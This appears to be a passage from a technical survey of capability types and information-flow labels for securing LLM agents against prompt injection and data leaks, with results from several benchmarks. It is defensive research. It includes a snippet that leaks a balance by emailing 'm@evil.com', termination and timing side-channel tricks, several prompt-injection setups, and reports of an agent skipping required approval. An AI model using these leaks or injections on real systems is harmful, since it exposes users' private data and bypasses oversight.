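
1. The closure uses fs, so its type is `() ->{fs} String`.
2. The closure is the block's result, so T would have to be `() ->{fs} String`.
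3. T is also the type of bad, which exists outside the block, where there is no fs. A type can mention only names that exist where it applies, so T can't be this type.

Declaring a vaguer type doesn't let a capability leave the block. *LACUNA* includes a case in which the developer asks for a function of type `String => String`, whose arrow normally allows any capability. The compiler still reports that the capability "outlives its scope", because a type outside the block can cover only capabilities that exist there. For the same reason, code can't put fs in a list that the block returns or store it in an outside variable. File handles obtained from fs have it in their capture sets, so they can't leave either.

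The rule also catches honest mistakes. Xu and colleagues describe a program that opens a file and starts a background computation to read it. The call that starts the computation returns immediately, so the block would end and the program would close the file before the computation finished reading it. The compiler rejects the program because the background computation captures the file. Opening the file inside the computation fixes the problem.

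In TACIT, requestFileSystem requires a capability for input and output, so a pure function can't use it to open a folder. However, the agent writes the folder's name into the request, and the type accepts any text, so the library has to enforce any limit on which folders an agent may request. Requests for network hosts and external commands work the same way.

### What the language has to guarantee

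Odersky and colleagues name three properties that a language needs before capture sets can support a security guarantee.

*Capability safety* means that code can neither forge a capability nor drop one from a type. Without it, a program could use an unchecked cast to change a function's type from `() ->{net} Unit` to `() -> Unit` and pass the function off as pure. Ordinary Scala allows such casts, so TACIT compiles agent code in safe mode.

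*Capability completeness* means that every effect that matters for safety requires a capability. Suppose one standard library function posted text to a web address and took only strings as arguments. Any function that called it would have an empty capture set, so the checker would accept it as pure even though it sent data out. This property is probably the hardest to secure, because it depends on every library function that an agent can reach. Odersky and colleagues don't require capabilities for effects that the harness can contain at run time. For example, TACIT converts exceptions into ordinary failure values instead of tracking them, because almost any code can fail with a division by zero.

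*Local purity* means that types can restrict one computation inside a larger program to a given set of capabilities, which may be empty. E and Joe-E lack it. Without it, a harness can deny network access to the step that handles contract text only by denying it to the whole program.

Haskell, by contrast, has types that separate pure functions from impure ones, but it has no built-in object capabilities. Odersky and colleagues expect that adding them would require advanced features such as linear types, which limit how often a program can use a value.

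### Directory tokens in ELBA

Zhou and colleagues get a good part of the way in Haskell with simpler means. Their file library for ELBA hides the function that builds a token, as the bibliography library did for trusted citations. The main operations are:

```
evalRIO  :: String -> RIO a -> IO a
(//)     :: Path -> String -> Path
readRIO  :: Path -> RIO String
writeRIO :: Path -> String -> RIO ()
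```

RIO is an effect type like BibIO, and a Path is a token for one folder or file and everything beneath it. The developer's code calls evalRIO with a root folder. Generated code of type RIO can't call evalRIO because evalRIO has an IO type, so every Path the generated code holds comes from that root. The expression `readRIO "/etc/passwd"` fails the type check because a string is not a Path.

The operator `//` narrows a token. If `root` covers a project folder, `root // "drafts"` covers only the drafts folder inside it. An agent could also write `root // "../salaries"`, where `..` means "one folder up". This passes the type check because the compiler doesn't inspect the disk. When the program runs, `//` works out the real location, following any links, and stops the program with an error if it is outside the project folder. The program may already have written other files by then.

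Like RIO, TACIT checks file paths at run time, but the two systems' types record different information. A Haskell function of type `String -> RIO ()` might hold a token for the drafts folder, a token for the whole project or no token, and its type is the same in each case. The developer can confine a step to the drafts by passing it only that token, as in E, but the compiler can't confirm that a function holds no other token. RIO's types also don't limit how long a program may keep a Path.

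Run-time tokens are more flexible than a fixed operating-system sandbox, which confines a whole process to one set of folders. A program can create, pass on and narrow tokens as it runs. Zhou and colleagues suggest that tokens could also stand for things other than folders, such as all the files on one branch of a code repository.

### Granting a sub-agent less

Capture sets give a parent agent a way to hand over only some of its permissions. Suppose that a parent in LACUNA holds docs, out and net, and wants a sub-agent to search the contracts without writing or sending anything. It could write:

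```
val findClause: () ->{docs} String =
  () => agent[String]("Find the termination clause in the contracts.")
```

LACUNA compiles the sub-agent's code in place, so the code becomes part of the body of findClause, whose capture set must be a subset of {docs}. If the sub-agent's code calls net.send, the body's capture set becomes {docs, net}, and the compiler rejects the code before any of it runs, even though the name net is visible there. As in ELBA, any agents the sub-agent starts are under the same limit or a stricter one. In LACUNA, this is because their code also becomes part of findClause. *LACUNA* uses the strictest form of this limit, in which a nested agent writes code inside a function that must be pure.

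In ELBA, a parent can ask a sub-agent for a function of type `Path -> RIO ()` and then apply it to `root // "drafts"`. The sub-agent's code receives the narrowed token and never has access to `root`.

Odersky and colleagues describe the same subset rule for TACIT but leave a full test with several agents to future work. The compiler enforces the grant as written and doesn't work out how small it could be. If a task needs permission to send mail, an attacker who misleads the model can still misuse that permission. *LACUNA* reports that attackers reached their goal in 8 of 1,898 trials with planted instructions and describes this result as consistent with that limit.

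### Functions stored in lists

Early versions of capture checking dealt badly with functions that a program stores in a list and calls later. They treated each item as if it were in a sealed box. A list of functions that print to the console counted as pure, and the console appeared in a capture set only when the program took a function out. This kept general-purpose code simple, because a function that counts the items in a list doesn't depend on what those items can do.

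However, the types had no name for the contents of the boxes. Xu and colleagues give the example of a function that takes a list of operations and returns an iterator, an object that produces results one at a time, in this case by running each operation in turn. The iterator can do whatever the operations can do, but the old system could not express that and rejected the function. Their solution is the *reach capability*, written with an asterisk:

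```
def mkIterator[T](@use ops: List[() => T]): Iterator[T]^{ops*}
```

Here `ops*` stands for everything that the operations in `ops` can use. If the caller passes a list of pure functions, the iterator is pure. If the operations print to the console, the iterator's capture set is `{console}`. `@use` tells the compiler that `mkIterator` opens the boxes, so their contents also count towards the capture set of the code that calls it. If a generated program hides a message-sending function in a list and passes the list to such a helper, the program's capture set therefore still includes `net`.

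An earlier attempt at reach capabilities in Scala 3 was seriously flawed because it accepted a function that returned any file it was given with a type that marked the file as pure. Xu and colleagues trace the mistake to confusion about which unknown set each `^` refers to. Their redesign translates every `^` into an explicit variable, and a computer has checked its soundness proof.

Reach capabilities are still coarse. If a pair holds one function that uses the network and another that uses files, a function that returns the network one gets a type that lists both capabilities. Some mutable collections also need an explicit parameter for the capabilities of their contents. Without it, the type of a collection that starts out empty would not allow adding functions that use capabilities.

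### Excluding a whole class of capabilities

A capture set can list the capabilities that a function may use, but it can't express "anything except the network". Scala's standard library needed such rules in two places. `Future` runs a computation on another thread, so the computation must not use anything tied to the original thread. `Try` runs a computation and catches any exception. It keeps the permission to throw, because it may rethrow the exception later, but it doesn't keep the files that the computation used.

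Pham and colleagues solve both cases with *classifiers*, tags arranged in a tree. Each capability has one tag and also counts as a member of every tag above it. Two operations then filter a capture set:

```
object Future:
  def apply[T](body: () ->{any.except[ThreadLocal]} T): Future[T]^{body}

object Try:
  def apply[T](body: () => T): Try[T]^{body.only[Control]}
```

Future accepts any computation that uses no thread-bound capabilities. The Control tag, which covers exceptions and similar jumps, is below ThreadLocal in the tree, so Future also excludes Control capabilities. The result of Try keeps only the Control capabilities of the computation it ran.

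Other libraries can add new tags to the tree beneath existing ones, and excluding a tag also excludes any tags added beneath it. For example, a harness developer could tag every kind of network connection as Network and accept only functions of type `() ->{any.except[Network]} Unit`. If a later library added a new kind of connection under that tag, the rule would exclude it without any change to the harness. An ordinary effect row can exclude individual effects or close the list entirely, but it can't exclude an open-ended category while still allowing all other effects.

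Filters can also apply to a single object. In an example from Google's cloud software, a function hands a database transaction to user code, which may do anything with it except commit it or roll it back. Classifiers restrict only that transaction, so the user code can still commit others. In Flix, a research language that can exclude effects by name, the corresponding type bans commits and rollbacks altogether. Pham and colleagues reproduced all 59 cases in an earlier collection of such exclusion patterns from real software.

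Flix is better than Scala's classifiers at relating two unknown sets. For example, Flix can require that two functions running in parallel have no effects in common. Classifiers can't express this, and Scala relies on a separate check for it. Because classifiers form a tree, a capability also can't have two unrelated tags, such as Read and Serializable.

### Capture sets and effect rows compared

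The main practical argument for capture checking concerns functions that take other functions as arguments. One example is map, whose effects are those of the function it applies to a list. Xu and colleagues set the type that map would need in an effect system with explicit parameters against its type under capture checking:

```
Effect parameter:   def map[U, E](f: T -> U eff E): List[U] eff E
Capture checking:   def map[U](f: T => U): List[U]
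```

The lower line is the type map has always had in Scala. It needs no effect parameter because the code that calls map must already have f. If f sends messages, its type lists net, so the calling code has net in its capture set before it calls map. The result type needs an annotation only if the result keeps a reference to f. For example, an iterator's map calls f later, each time the program reads another item, so its result has the type `Iterator[B]^{this, f}`.

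This matters most for an established language whose libraries contain thousands of published function types. Koka's compiler infers effect rows, so programmers don't have to write many of them either.

Capture sets describe operations less precisely than rows do. The row of the contract program is {Docs.read, Model.ask, Out.write}, while its capture set in TACIT would be {docs, out}, since TACIT treats the summarising model as pure. If docs also had a method for deleting contracts, a program that deleted them all would have the same capture set. The developer can prevent this by providing an object that can only read or by tagging the two kinds of access with different classifiers. Capture sets do distinguish two files of the same type without extra work, and Eff's rows can too.

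The check also counts mentioning a function as using it. The expression `() => f` returns f without calling it, but its capture set still includes f. Xu and colleagues found that this caused no serious problems when they adapted Scala's library.

### Measurements on Scala's standard library

Xu and colleagues converted all of Scala's standard collections (lists, sets, maps and so on) to capture checking, along with some basic language types. These results describe the converted code:

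| Measure | Result |
|---|---|
| Functions whose signatures needed capture sets | 691 of 6,189 (11%) |
| Classes that needed capture sets | 91 of 684 (13%) |
| Lines of code added or rewritten | 1,418 of 31,395 (4.5%) |
| Reach capabilities written out | 19 |
| Unsafe casts and unsafe removals of capture sets | 30 |
| Compile time spent on capture checking | 3.9 of 29.2 seconds (13%) |

The paper reports that about 3% of lines changed, which matches the count if the total includes comments and blank lines. Either way, the burden is small for code of this kind, and about half of the changed signatures only needed a `^` to allow arguments that carry capabilities. The 30 unsafe steps matter more for security than their number suggests, because at each one the compiler relies on a programmer's unchecked claim that a capability can be ignored, so these steps are part of the trusted base.

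Pham and colleagues used classifiers and related library changes to raise the share of the standard library's code that compiles under capture checking from 66.7% to 81.7%. Classifiers account for only part of the increase, though Try and Future could not have precise types without them. The library now contains 14 uses of `.only` and 151 of `.except`, which programmers must write by hand because the compiler never infers them. Pham and colleagues noticed no slowdown from classifiers but have not run a dedicated performance study.

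The designers of capture checking did both conversions themselves, so the figures don't show how easily other programmers or language models would write these types. An agent's snippet would usually need fewer annotations than a library, because the compiler infers most capture sets inside a program and the harness developer writes the signatures of the functions the agent calls.

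## Keeping secret data from leaking through permitted actions

An agent that may read a file and use the network can send the file to anyone it can reach. Both actions are on its list, so the subset test passes. Narrower permissions only partly prevent this. If the contract agent's job includes mailing a short notice to a client, it needs both `docs` and `net`, and neither an effect row nor a capture set (the capabilities a value may use) distinguishes sending the notice from sending the full text of the contract.

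An agent can leak data without a mail tool, because its model usually runs on a provider's servers and the harness sends that model whatever the agent's program prints. Odersky and colleagues point out that a sandbox doesn't catch this. The agent reads a private file with one permitted call and contacts the cloud model with another, and only the movement of data between the calls is wrong. *Information-flow control* therefore restricts where data may travel rather than which actions may run.

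### Noninterference

The usual goal of information-flow control is *noninterference*, which Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer formulated in 1982. It requires that a program's public outputs don't depend on its secret inputs. To make this exact, write P(s, p) for the public output of a program P with secret input s and public input p. The program is noninterfering if

P(s₁, p) = P(s₂, p)  for all secrets s₁, s₂ and every public input p

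A program keeps a secret if someone who sees only its public output can't learn anything about the secret. A program that prints a secret contract fails this test. So does one that prints "long" if the contract has more than ten pages and "short" otherwise, even though it never copies any of the text. The second leak is an *implicit flow*, in which the secret determines which branch of the program runs and the branch determines the output.

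Most systems enforce noninterference with labels on data. The relation L₁ ⊑ L₂ means that data labelled L₁ can flow to a place labelled L₂, so public ⊑ secret but not the reverse. Combining data labelled L₁ with data labelled L₂ gives a result labelled L₁ ⊔ L₂, the lowest label to which both can flow. *SPA* (2026), a paper on agents that keep data between requests, distinguishes confidentiality labels, which keep sensitive data away from unauthorised destinations, from integrity labels, which keep untrustworthy data, such as a stranger's email, from influencing actions that need trusted input. An injected instruction that makes an agent mail out a contract violates both confidentiality and integrity.

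Noninterference is too strict for many useful agents. Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, describes an assistant that answers meeting requests with the user's availability, so its answers depend on a private calendar, as the user intended. The standard remedy is *declassification*, a rule specifying what a program may release, but somebody has to write the rule for each task. Dongol instead compares the agent with a reference agent that runs the same plan and never obeys instructions in untrusted text. The agent passes if, whenever an attacker can tell two possible secrets apart, some input to the reference agent would also have told them apart. Tricking the assistant into adding a password-reset code therefore counts as a leak, but tricking it into sending the calendar doesn't, because a genuine meeting request would have obtained the calendar too. The comparison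 requires a plan that is fixed before the agent reads anything untrusted, so it doesn't cover agents that choose each step after seeing the result of the last one.

### Sealed values in TACIT

TACIT protects confidential text with a wrapper type called `Classified`. The developer designates certain folders as classified, and the agent's program receives the contents of files in them as a `Classified[String]` instead of a `String`. In the contract scenario, the wrapper has three methods:

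```
class Classified[T]:
  def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
  def aggregate[U](x: Classified[U]): Classified[(T, U)]
  def reveal(using permission: CanAccess[T]): T
```

The agent holds no `CanAccess` capability, so it can't call `reveal`. It works on the text through `map`, which applies a function to the contents and seals the result. The arrow `->` restricts `map` to pure functions:

```
val contract = readClassified("secret/contract.txt")
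contract.map(text => text.toUpperCase)              // accepted
contract.map(text => { net.send(text); text })      // rejected: uses net
```

Because the function is pure, it can't leak the text directly by printing it or writing it to a file. It also can't store the text in an outside variable, because safe mode tracks changes to variables too. Only the function's result leaves it, and `map` keeps that result secret.

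The wrapper also stops implicit flows. A test such as `text.length > 10000` inside `map` produces a `Classified[Boolean]`, but Scala's `if` needs an ordinary Boolean, so the agent's program can't send one message for long contracts and another for short ones. The program also can't detect long contracts by throwing an exception for them and checking for the failure, because TACIT can seal the failure value like any other result.

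This part of the protection is static, but whether a file arrives sealed depends on where it is stored. A password saved outside the classified folders arrives as a plain string. The type also has only one level of secrecy. A `Classified[String]` doesn't record whose secret it holds, so the compiler accepts a program that combines the contracts of two rival clients.

### Printing and summarising sealed text

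TACIT's print function writes to two channels so that the user can see sealed results without revealing them to the cloud model. One channel goes to the agent and from there to the cloud model, and the other goes only to the user's terminal. Both carry the same text for ordinary values, but for a sealed value the agent's channel carries only `Classified(****)`.

Odersky and colleagues illustrate this with a two-turn conversation. The agent first has a contract summarised and prints the result, which only the user can read. The user then asks how long the summary is. The agent runs `summary.map(_.length)` and prints the length, which again only the user can see. The agent's access to the folder ended with the first turn, but its program can still use the sealed summary.

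Summarizing the contract requires a language model that can read it. TACIT's `chat` function lets the agent's program call a separate, trusted model, which could run on the user's own machine. The answer is sealed if the text passed to `chat` is sealed, and is otherwise an ordinary string. The trusted model has no tools, so an instruction planted in the contract can't make it send anything. The instruction could still make it write a false summary, which the user would read. The agent couldn't detect the problem, because it sees only asterisks whether the summary is good, false or missing.

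### Labels that rise in ELBA

ELBA's approach to secrets relies on LIO, an existing Haskell library that Stefan, Russo and colleagues (2012), in *Flexible Dynamic Information Flow Control in the Presence of Exceptions*, describe in detail. LIO keeps one *current label* for the whole running computation, which covers every value the computation has in hand. *On Dynamic Flow-Sensitive Floating-Label Systems* (2015) gives the two main rules:

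```
Reading data labelled d:           current label becomes  current ⊔ d
Writing to a place labelled e:     allowed only if        current ⊑ e
```

Suppose a program starts with a public label and reads a secret contract. Its label rises to secret, and LIO then blocks every write to a public web address, even if the message is just "hello". LIO doesn't need to check whether the message contains any of the contract. Implicit flows need no extra rule, because a program must read a secret before branching on it, and reading it raises the label.

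ELBA's labels record who may see a piece of data and which sources have influenced it. In an example from Zhou and colleagues, a program fetches a page from phony.com and tries to write the contents to the user. The fetch lowers the computation's integrity to that of phony.com, so LIO stops the write. Unlike TACIT's single seal, these labels can also keep one customer's data apart from another's.

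ELBA's protection is part static and part dynamic. Before a program runs, the compiler checks that the program has LIO's effect type, so it can use only the labelled operations and not Haskell's ordinary file and network functions. LIO computes and compares the labels while the program runs, so a program can compile, post one message, read a web page and then stop with an error at its second message. Stefan and colleagues chose run-time labels because static analysis works poorly when new users and new kinds of data keep appearing.

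If a program's label can only rise, reading one web page is enough to block most later actions. LIO's `toLabeled` function avoids this by running part of the program separately. The label rises inside that part, but the outer label doesn't change, and the result comes back sealed in a `Labeled` value. The programmer has to name the result's label in advance, and the separate part can't read anything above it. LIO can also set a *clearance*, an upper limit on the current label, which prevents a computation from reading certain data at all.

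### Two models and a run-time tracker

TACIT's trusted model and LIO's separate computations both resemble the *dual-LLM pattern*, which the programmer Simon Willison proposed in 2023. Only a quarantined model without tools reads untrusted text. A privileged model has the tools and refers to the quarantined model's answers by name, without seeing them, so instructions hidden in the text never reach a model that could carry them out.

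An ELBA program gets the same separation by calling a sub-agent inside `toLabeled`. Zhou and colleagues describe a sub-agent that reads untrusted data and drafts a direct message. The outer agent passes the sealed draft to a sending function, which checks the labels of the message and the recipient. The sub-agent can keep its tools, because LIO limits what it can do with them once it has read untrusted data.

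CaMeL, which Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues presented in 2025, combines the dual-LLM pattern with code. Before any untrusted data arrives, the privileged model writes a whole program in a subset of Python without user-defined functions. A custom interpreter runs the program and tracks where each value came from. When the program calls a tool, the interpreter checks that record against a policy. An injected instruction cannot add a step because the program is already written, but it could still change a value, such as the recipient of a payment, and the tracking is meant to catch such changes.

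Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, found two gaps in CaMeL's tracking. The first is an old trick from the 1970s. Written out in full, it looks like this:

```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold: tmp  = False
if tmp:                         rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL marks a variable as secret when the program assigns to it inside a branch that depends on a secret. If the balance is high, the third line sets `tmp` to False, and CaMeL marks `tmp` as secret. The program then skips the fourth line, so `rich` stays True and unmarked. The last line appears to depend only on public data, so CaMeL allows the email. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes False and the program sends no email. The attacker learns whether the balance is high from whether the email is sent, because CaMeL can't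 mark a variable when the program skips the assignment to it.

The second gap is in the loop around the interpreter. When a policy stops a program, ordinary Python code that CaMeL doesn't track prompts the model to try again. Whether the policy stops a run can depend on a secret, so each run can leak one bit, and an attacker who can trigger many retries can extract the whole secret. TACIT's compiler retries don't leak this way, because whether the compiler rejects a program depends on the code and never on the contents of the contract.

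### A proof for agents that write code

Garby and colleagues designed a small language for agents, LLMbda, whose label tracking they could prove correct. It has no static types. Every value carries a label, and a single label covers the whole conversation with the model. When the model writes code, the interpreter runs it under the conversation's label, so if a secret has entered the conversation, everything the code computes also counts as secret.

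The language also closes CaMeL's first gap. One of Garby and colleagues' test programs sends the model a message that x is false, then, if a secret bit is set, a second message that x is true, and finally asks for x. The interpreter stops the program at the second message, because code that depends on a secret may not add to a public conversation. Otherwise the program runs to the end, so an observer can still learn one bit from whether it finishes. Unlike CaMeL, LLMbda also tracks the retry loop, so nobody can repeat this leak freely.

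Proving noninterference here takes some care, because a language model gives different answers to the same prompt. The theorem has to compare probabilities. Let μ₁(r) and μ₂(r) be the probabilities of a public result r under two different secrets. They may add up to less than 1, and the missing part is the chance that the program never finishes or gets stopped. The theorem states that there is always a single assignment of probabilities ω, with a total of at most 1, such that

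μ₁(r) ≤ ω(r)  and  μ₂(r) ≤ ω(r)  for every result r

If the program always finishes, both totals are already 1, so μ₁ and μ₂ must be equal and the result reveals nothing. The condition is much weaker for programs that often hang. Suppose a program prints "yes" half the time under one secret and "no" half the time under the other, and otherwise runs forever. Setting ω to one half for each answer satisfies the condition, even though anyone who gets an answer learns the secret. Garby and colleagues prove that the statistical distance between the two cases is at most their average chance of not finishing, which is one half here.

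The proof constructs ω with a second version of the interpreter, which skips any part of the program as soon as that part's label becomes secret and uses a dummy value instead. This version never uses the secrets, so it gives the same probabilities whatever the secrets are. Skipping can only make a program finish more often, so these probabilities are at least as large as μ₁ and μ₂. The proof assistant Lean has checked the argument, which covers every program in the language, including agents that generate and run new code. CaMeL has no comparable theorem.

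LLMbda lets a developer make an exception for data they decide to trust, using the command `endorse` to raise its integrity. For instance, a quarantined model might sort an untrusted email into one of eight categories, and the program might endorse the category so that it can appear in the subject line of a reply. An attacker who controls the email can choose the category, which gives them at most three bits of influence. A second theorem shows that endorsing data this way can't weaken the protection of secrets. Both theorems take the labels on incoming data as given, and LLMbda so far represents tools as functions inside the program, not as real outside services.

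The four systems divide the work as follows:

| System | Before the program runs | While the program runs |
|---|---|---|
| TACIT | the compiler checks that functions on sealed data are pure | the library seals files and redacts printed values |
| ELBA with LIO | the compiler checks that the program uses only labelled operations | LIO raises the current label and checks writes |
| CaMeL | no type check of data flows | the interpreter tracks values and checks tool calls |
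| LLMbda | no type check; the theorem covers all programs | the interpreter tracks values and the conversation |

### TACIT's leak test

Odersky and colleagues tested the seal on a sample software project with a folder of API keys, a database and confidential documents. They wrote 12 ordinary user tasks and 10 injection attacks, from simple instructions in code comments to fake system messages and ready-made Scala code for reading the secrets. Pairing every task with every attack gave 120 trials. In another 11 trials, the user asked for the secrets, either directly or while posing as someone in authority. Each model went through all 131 trials twice, once with sealed files and once with plain strings. The table gives the share of trials in which no secret appeared in the agent's output:

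| Model | Trials | Sealed | Plain strings |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 with injections | 100% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 81.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | all 131 | 100% | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 with injections | 100% | 97.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 27.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | all 131 | 100% | 91.6% |

Without the seal, Sonnet leaked secrets in 2 trials and MiniMax in 11, mostly because the user asked for them. Sonnet resisted every injection attack even without the seal, so the 120 injection trials hardly tested the seal for that model. On their own, 131 trials without a leak would rule out only leak rates above about 2%. The argument from purity is stronger evidence, and the trials mainly check that the software implements purity properly.

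Sealing the files did not reduce the share of user tasks completed. Sonnet completed 99.2% of them with sealed files and 83.3% with plain strings, while MiniMax completed 90.0% and 88.3%, respectively. Odersky and colleagues suggest that Sonnet's gap is an artefact of their setup, in which it often ran out of turns or time, or stopped to warn the user about an injection.

### Results on AgentDojo

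The AgentDojo benchmark covers a wider range of attacks, including ones that try to trigger an action without stealing any data. Odersky and colleagues moved its four sets of tasks (banking, office work, Slack messages and travel) to TACIT and ran 963 attack trials with each of two models, Gemini 2.5 Pro and o4-mini-high. AgentDojo scored one of the 1,926 trials as a successful attack. In that trial, the user asked to book one hotel, and the attacker had planted a recommendation for another in its reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews word for word, which put the other hotel's name in its answer. Odersky and colleagues attribute the score to AgentDojo's text matching, since the policy allows public reviews to reach the user. Their explanation is convincing, and Garby and colleagues report that CaMeL failed a travel trial for the same reason.

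It is harder to tell how much TACIT's types contributed, because the same agents weren't tested without them. Zhou and colleagues did make that comparison for ELBA on the Slack tasks, and all four of their models resisted all 105 attacks with the policies switched off. Recent models resist AgentDojo's standard attacks too easily for those attacks to show whether a defence works.

Zhou and colleagues therefore made the attacks succeed at the first step. They changed ELBA so that when a sub-agent received data containing the marker "TODO:", which AgentDojo's direct attacks use, the harness threw away the sub-agent's real task and gave it only the attacker's text. The sub-agent then treated the attack as its instructions. The Slack set has 21 user tasks and 5 injections, which makes 105 pairs, and seven runs of each pair give the 735 trials per model in this table:

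| Model | Attacks resisted, with policies | Attacks resisted, without | Tasks completed, with policies | Tasks completed, without |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 735 | 425 | 351 | 523 |
| Opus 4.8 | 735 | 460 | 312 | 557 |
| GPT 5.4 | 735 | 621 | 338 | 558 |
| Sonnet 5 | 735 | 540 | 294 | 494 |

This is the most informative of the AgentDojo tests because up to 42% of the attacks succeeded without the policies. The perfect scores include a manual correction. AgentDojo counted 29 of the 2,940 runs with policies as successful attacks because an agent had opened a fixed web address. Zhou and colleagues reviewed all 29 and found no leaked data or policy violations.

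The 735 trials also have limited variety because they repeat the same five injections. These come from AgentDojo and weren't designed to target ELBA. An attacker who knew ELBA's policies would look for mistakes in them. The label rules would still apply, but they can't correct a wrong label or a policy that allows too much.

Garby and colleagues ran the banking tasks with an LLMbda agent called Randori, which tries each plan on a simulated account before using the real one. Across three models, 2 of 1,296 attacks succeeded. In both, the user had asked the agent to pay a bill according to a text file, and the attacker had replaced the file with a different payment request. The agent had endorsed the file's contents, so the labels no longer blocked the payment. Removing the `endorse` command stopped the attack, but the agent could then no longer do the task even when the file was genuine.

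They also sorted AgentDojo's 144 banking pairs by what the attack needs. In 97 of them, the attack needs a tool that a plan for the user's task would never contain, so writing the plan before reading any untrusted data is normally enough to defeat it. Only the other 47 test the label tracking. TACIT and ELBA let the agent write more code after reading data, so they can't rely on an early plan and need their types and labels against all of these attacks.

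### The cost in completed tasks

In ELBA's test with compromised sub-agents, the policies reduced the number of completed tasks by 33% to 44%. The loss is about as large without attacks, so the attacks explain little of it. The next table shows the ranges across models for tasks without attacks. Zhou and colleagues ran the Slack tasks, and Garby and colleagues ran the banking tasks three times each.

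| System | Tasks | Completed without policies | Completed with policies |
|---|---|---|---|
| ELBA | Slack, 21 | 14–18 | 8–10 |
| CaMeL | Slack, 21 | 13–17 | 4–6 |
| CaMeL | banking, 48 | 32–34 | 18 |
| Randori | banking, 48 | not tested | 31–36 |

A strict integrity policy forbids many ordinary requests. If a user asks the agent to read a web page and post a summary to a channel, untrusted text has to influence the message. The policy forbids this even when the influence is harmless, because the labels don't record whether it is. Zhou and colleagues suggest that the agent ask a person for approval only when such a policy would block an action. Randori completes more tasks because its plans can endorse data, but the two payment attacks show the risk of allowing this. The two models that Garby and colleagues retested completed 36 and 31 of the 48 tasks with endorsement, and 30 and 26 without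 it.

These samples are small. With the policies on, ELBA completed more Slack tasks than CaMeL for every model. But there were only 21 tasks, and the 95% confidence interval for one model's gap runs from 7 percentage points in CaMeL's favour to 34 in ELBA's. The comparison is clearer in the attacked runs, which have more trials.

TACIT's results on AgentDojo vary so much that an overall comparison with CaMeL means little. Odersky and colleagues call the two systems' task completion comparable, but with o4-mini-high, TACIT completed 52.9% of the office tasks and CaMeL 81.4%. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT completed 64.3% of the travel tasks and CaMeL 1.4%. The CaMeL figures come from CaMeL's own paper, so differences in prompts and setup may explain part of these gaps.

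### Timing and termination

Labels and seals control the values a program passes on, but its running time also reveals information. *Proving the Absence of Microarchitectural Timing Channels* (2023) defines a *covert channel* as a flow of information through a mechanism not intended for that purpose. A covert channel is a *side channel* if an attacker can use it to extract a secret from an innocent program. Other covert channels need an insider who deliberately sends the signal. In an agent system, a misled or hostile model can be that insider, because the model writes the program.

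Odersky and colleagues exclude timing and termination from TACIT's guarantee. This line shows why:

```
contract.map(text => if text.contains("merger") then slow(text) else text)
```

If `slow` is a pure function that takes ten seconds, the compiler accepts the line. The result is sealed, but anyone who times the call learns whether the contract mentions a merger. Odersky and colleagues say this leaks a single bit, which is correct for one call. But an agent can make many calls in a session, and twenty yes-or-no answers are enough to identify one possibility in a million.

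A program can send the same signal by never finishing. Most practical systems accept this and prove only *termination-insensitive* noninterference, which ignores whatever an observer learns from whether a program ends. According to *Generalizing Permissive-Upgrade in Dynamic Information Flow Analysis* (2015), this tolerates a leak of one bit if the observer sees only the final result, and possibly more if the program produces output along the way. A program with a sealed four-digit PIN could do the following:

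```
for i <- 0 to 9999 do
  println(i)
  pin.map(p => if p == i then loopForever() else p)
```

The function inside `map` is pure, and the printed numbers are public. If the agent's side can watch the output as it appears, the last number it sees is the PIN. Counting like this would take far too long for a cryptographic key, but an attacker who can restart the program could test one bit of the key on each run.

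LIO and LLMbda are also termination-insensitive. In an example much like the merger test, Stefan and colleagues describe a program that loops forever if a confidential review begins with certain words. They prevent this leak by setting the program's clearance too low for it to read the review. This works for data that a task doesn't need, but not for a contract that the agent has to summarise.

A stricter alternative, which *Nonmalleable Progress Leakage* (2025) calls progress-sensitive noninterference, doesn't let termination leak anything. But many legitimate programs contain loops that depend on secret data, and *Reconciling Shannon and Scott with a Lattice of Computable Information* (2022) explains that the termination-insensitive version is more permissive because it allows such loops. Even a progress-sensitive guarantee doesn't necessarily cover how long a program takes to finish. Timing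 is hard to control in much simpler systems too. The information-flow proofs for seL4, a small, formally verified operating-system kernel, don't address it.

Timing can reveal a secret even when a person approves every message. In one of Dongol's examples, Alice approves the exact text of a reply, and each approval covers one message. An injected instruction makes the model try to send some private data just before the planned reply. If the data differ from the approved text, the monitor blocks the attempt and the reply goes out. If they are identical, the monitor lets the injected message through and blocks the planned one. The attacker receives the same single message in both cases, but it arrives one step earlier when the private data match Alice's reply, which reveals the match.

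## Requiring actions to happen in a set order

A harness that needs a person's approval for a change has to ask before making it. Tan and colleagues cite a bug report in which Goose, an open-source coding agent, didn't ask. The user's session required approval for sensitive tools, but when Goose handed work to a sub-agent, the sub-agent started in automatic mode and ran those tools without asking the user. A list of permitted effects would not have prevented this, because the session allowed the tools as long as the agent asked first.

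### What a set of effects leaves out

Suppose an agent reviews some code and proposes a patch p. The harness could apply the patch like this:

```
let ok = perform Approval.request(p) in
if ok then perform Repo.apply(p) else ()
```

Approval.request asks a person for approval and returns true or false, and Repo.apply changes the files. A program that calls Approval.request and then Repo.apply has the row {Approval.request, Repo.apply}. If a later edit swaps the two calls, the program changes the files before asking, but its row stays the same because a set has no order. Checking the row against a set of permitted operations therefore can't accept the first version and reject the second.

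A developer who tries out a workflow in a dry run also wants to know whether the real run would ask for approval before writing. But the dry run's row contains no write, so a rule about writes doesn't apply to it.

An agent can also be told that it is in a simulation when its actions have real effects. Tan and colleagues cite a cybersecurity test in which the operators told Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5 that it was working in an offline simulation. A configuration error had left the internet reachable, and the model published a malicious package to PyPI, the public index of Python software. A rule that forbids publishing even in a simulation still applies when the environment isn't actually isolated.

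### A row and a request summary

ETAS therefore gives every program two records. Its judgment extends the one used so far:

Γ ⊢ e : τ ! ε ▷ A

The row ε lists the effects that can reach the outside world, after handlers have removed the ones they absorb. The *request summary* A describes the sequences of requests that the program may make, including those that a handler inside the program answers. The notation for A is close to the regular expressions that programmers use to search text:

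| Notation | Sequences it describes |
|---|---|
| 1 | the empty sequence, with no requests |
| op | a single request for op |
| A ; B | a sequence from A followed by one from B |
| A ⊔ B | a sequence from A or one from B |
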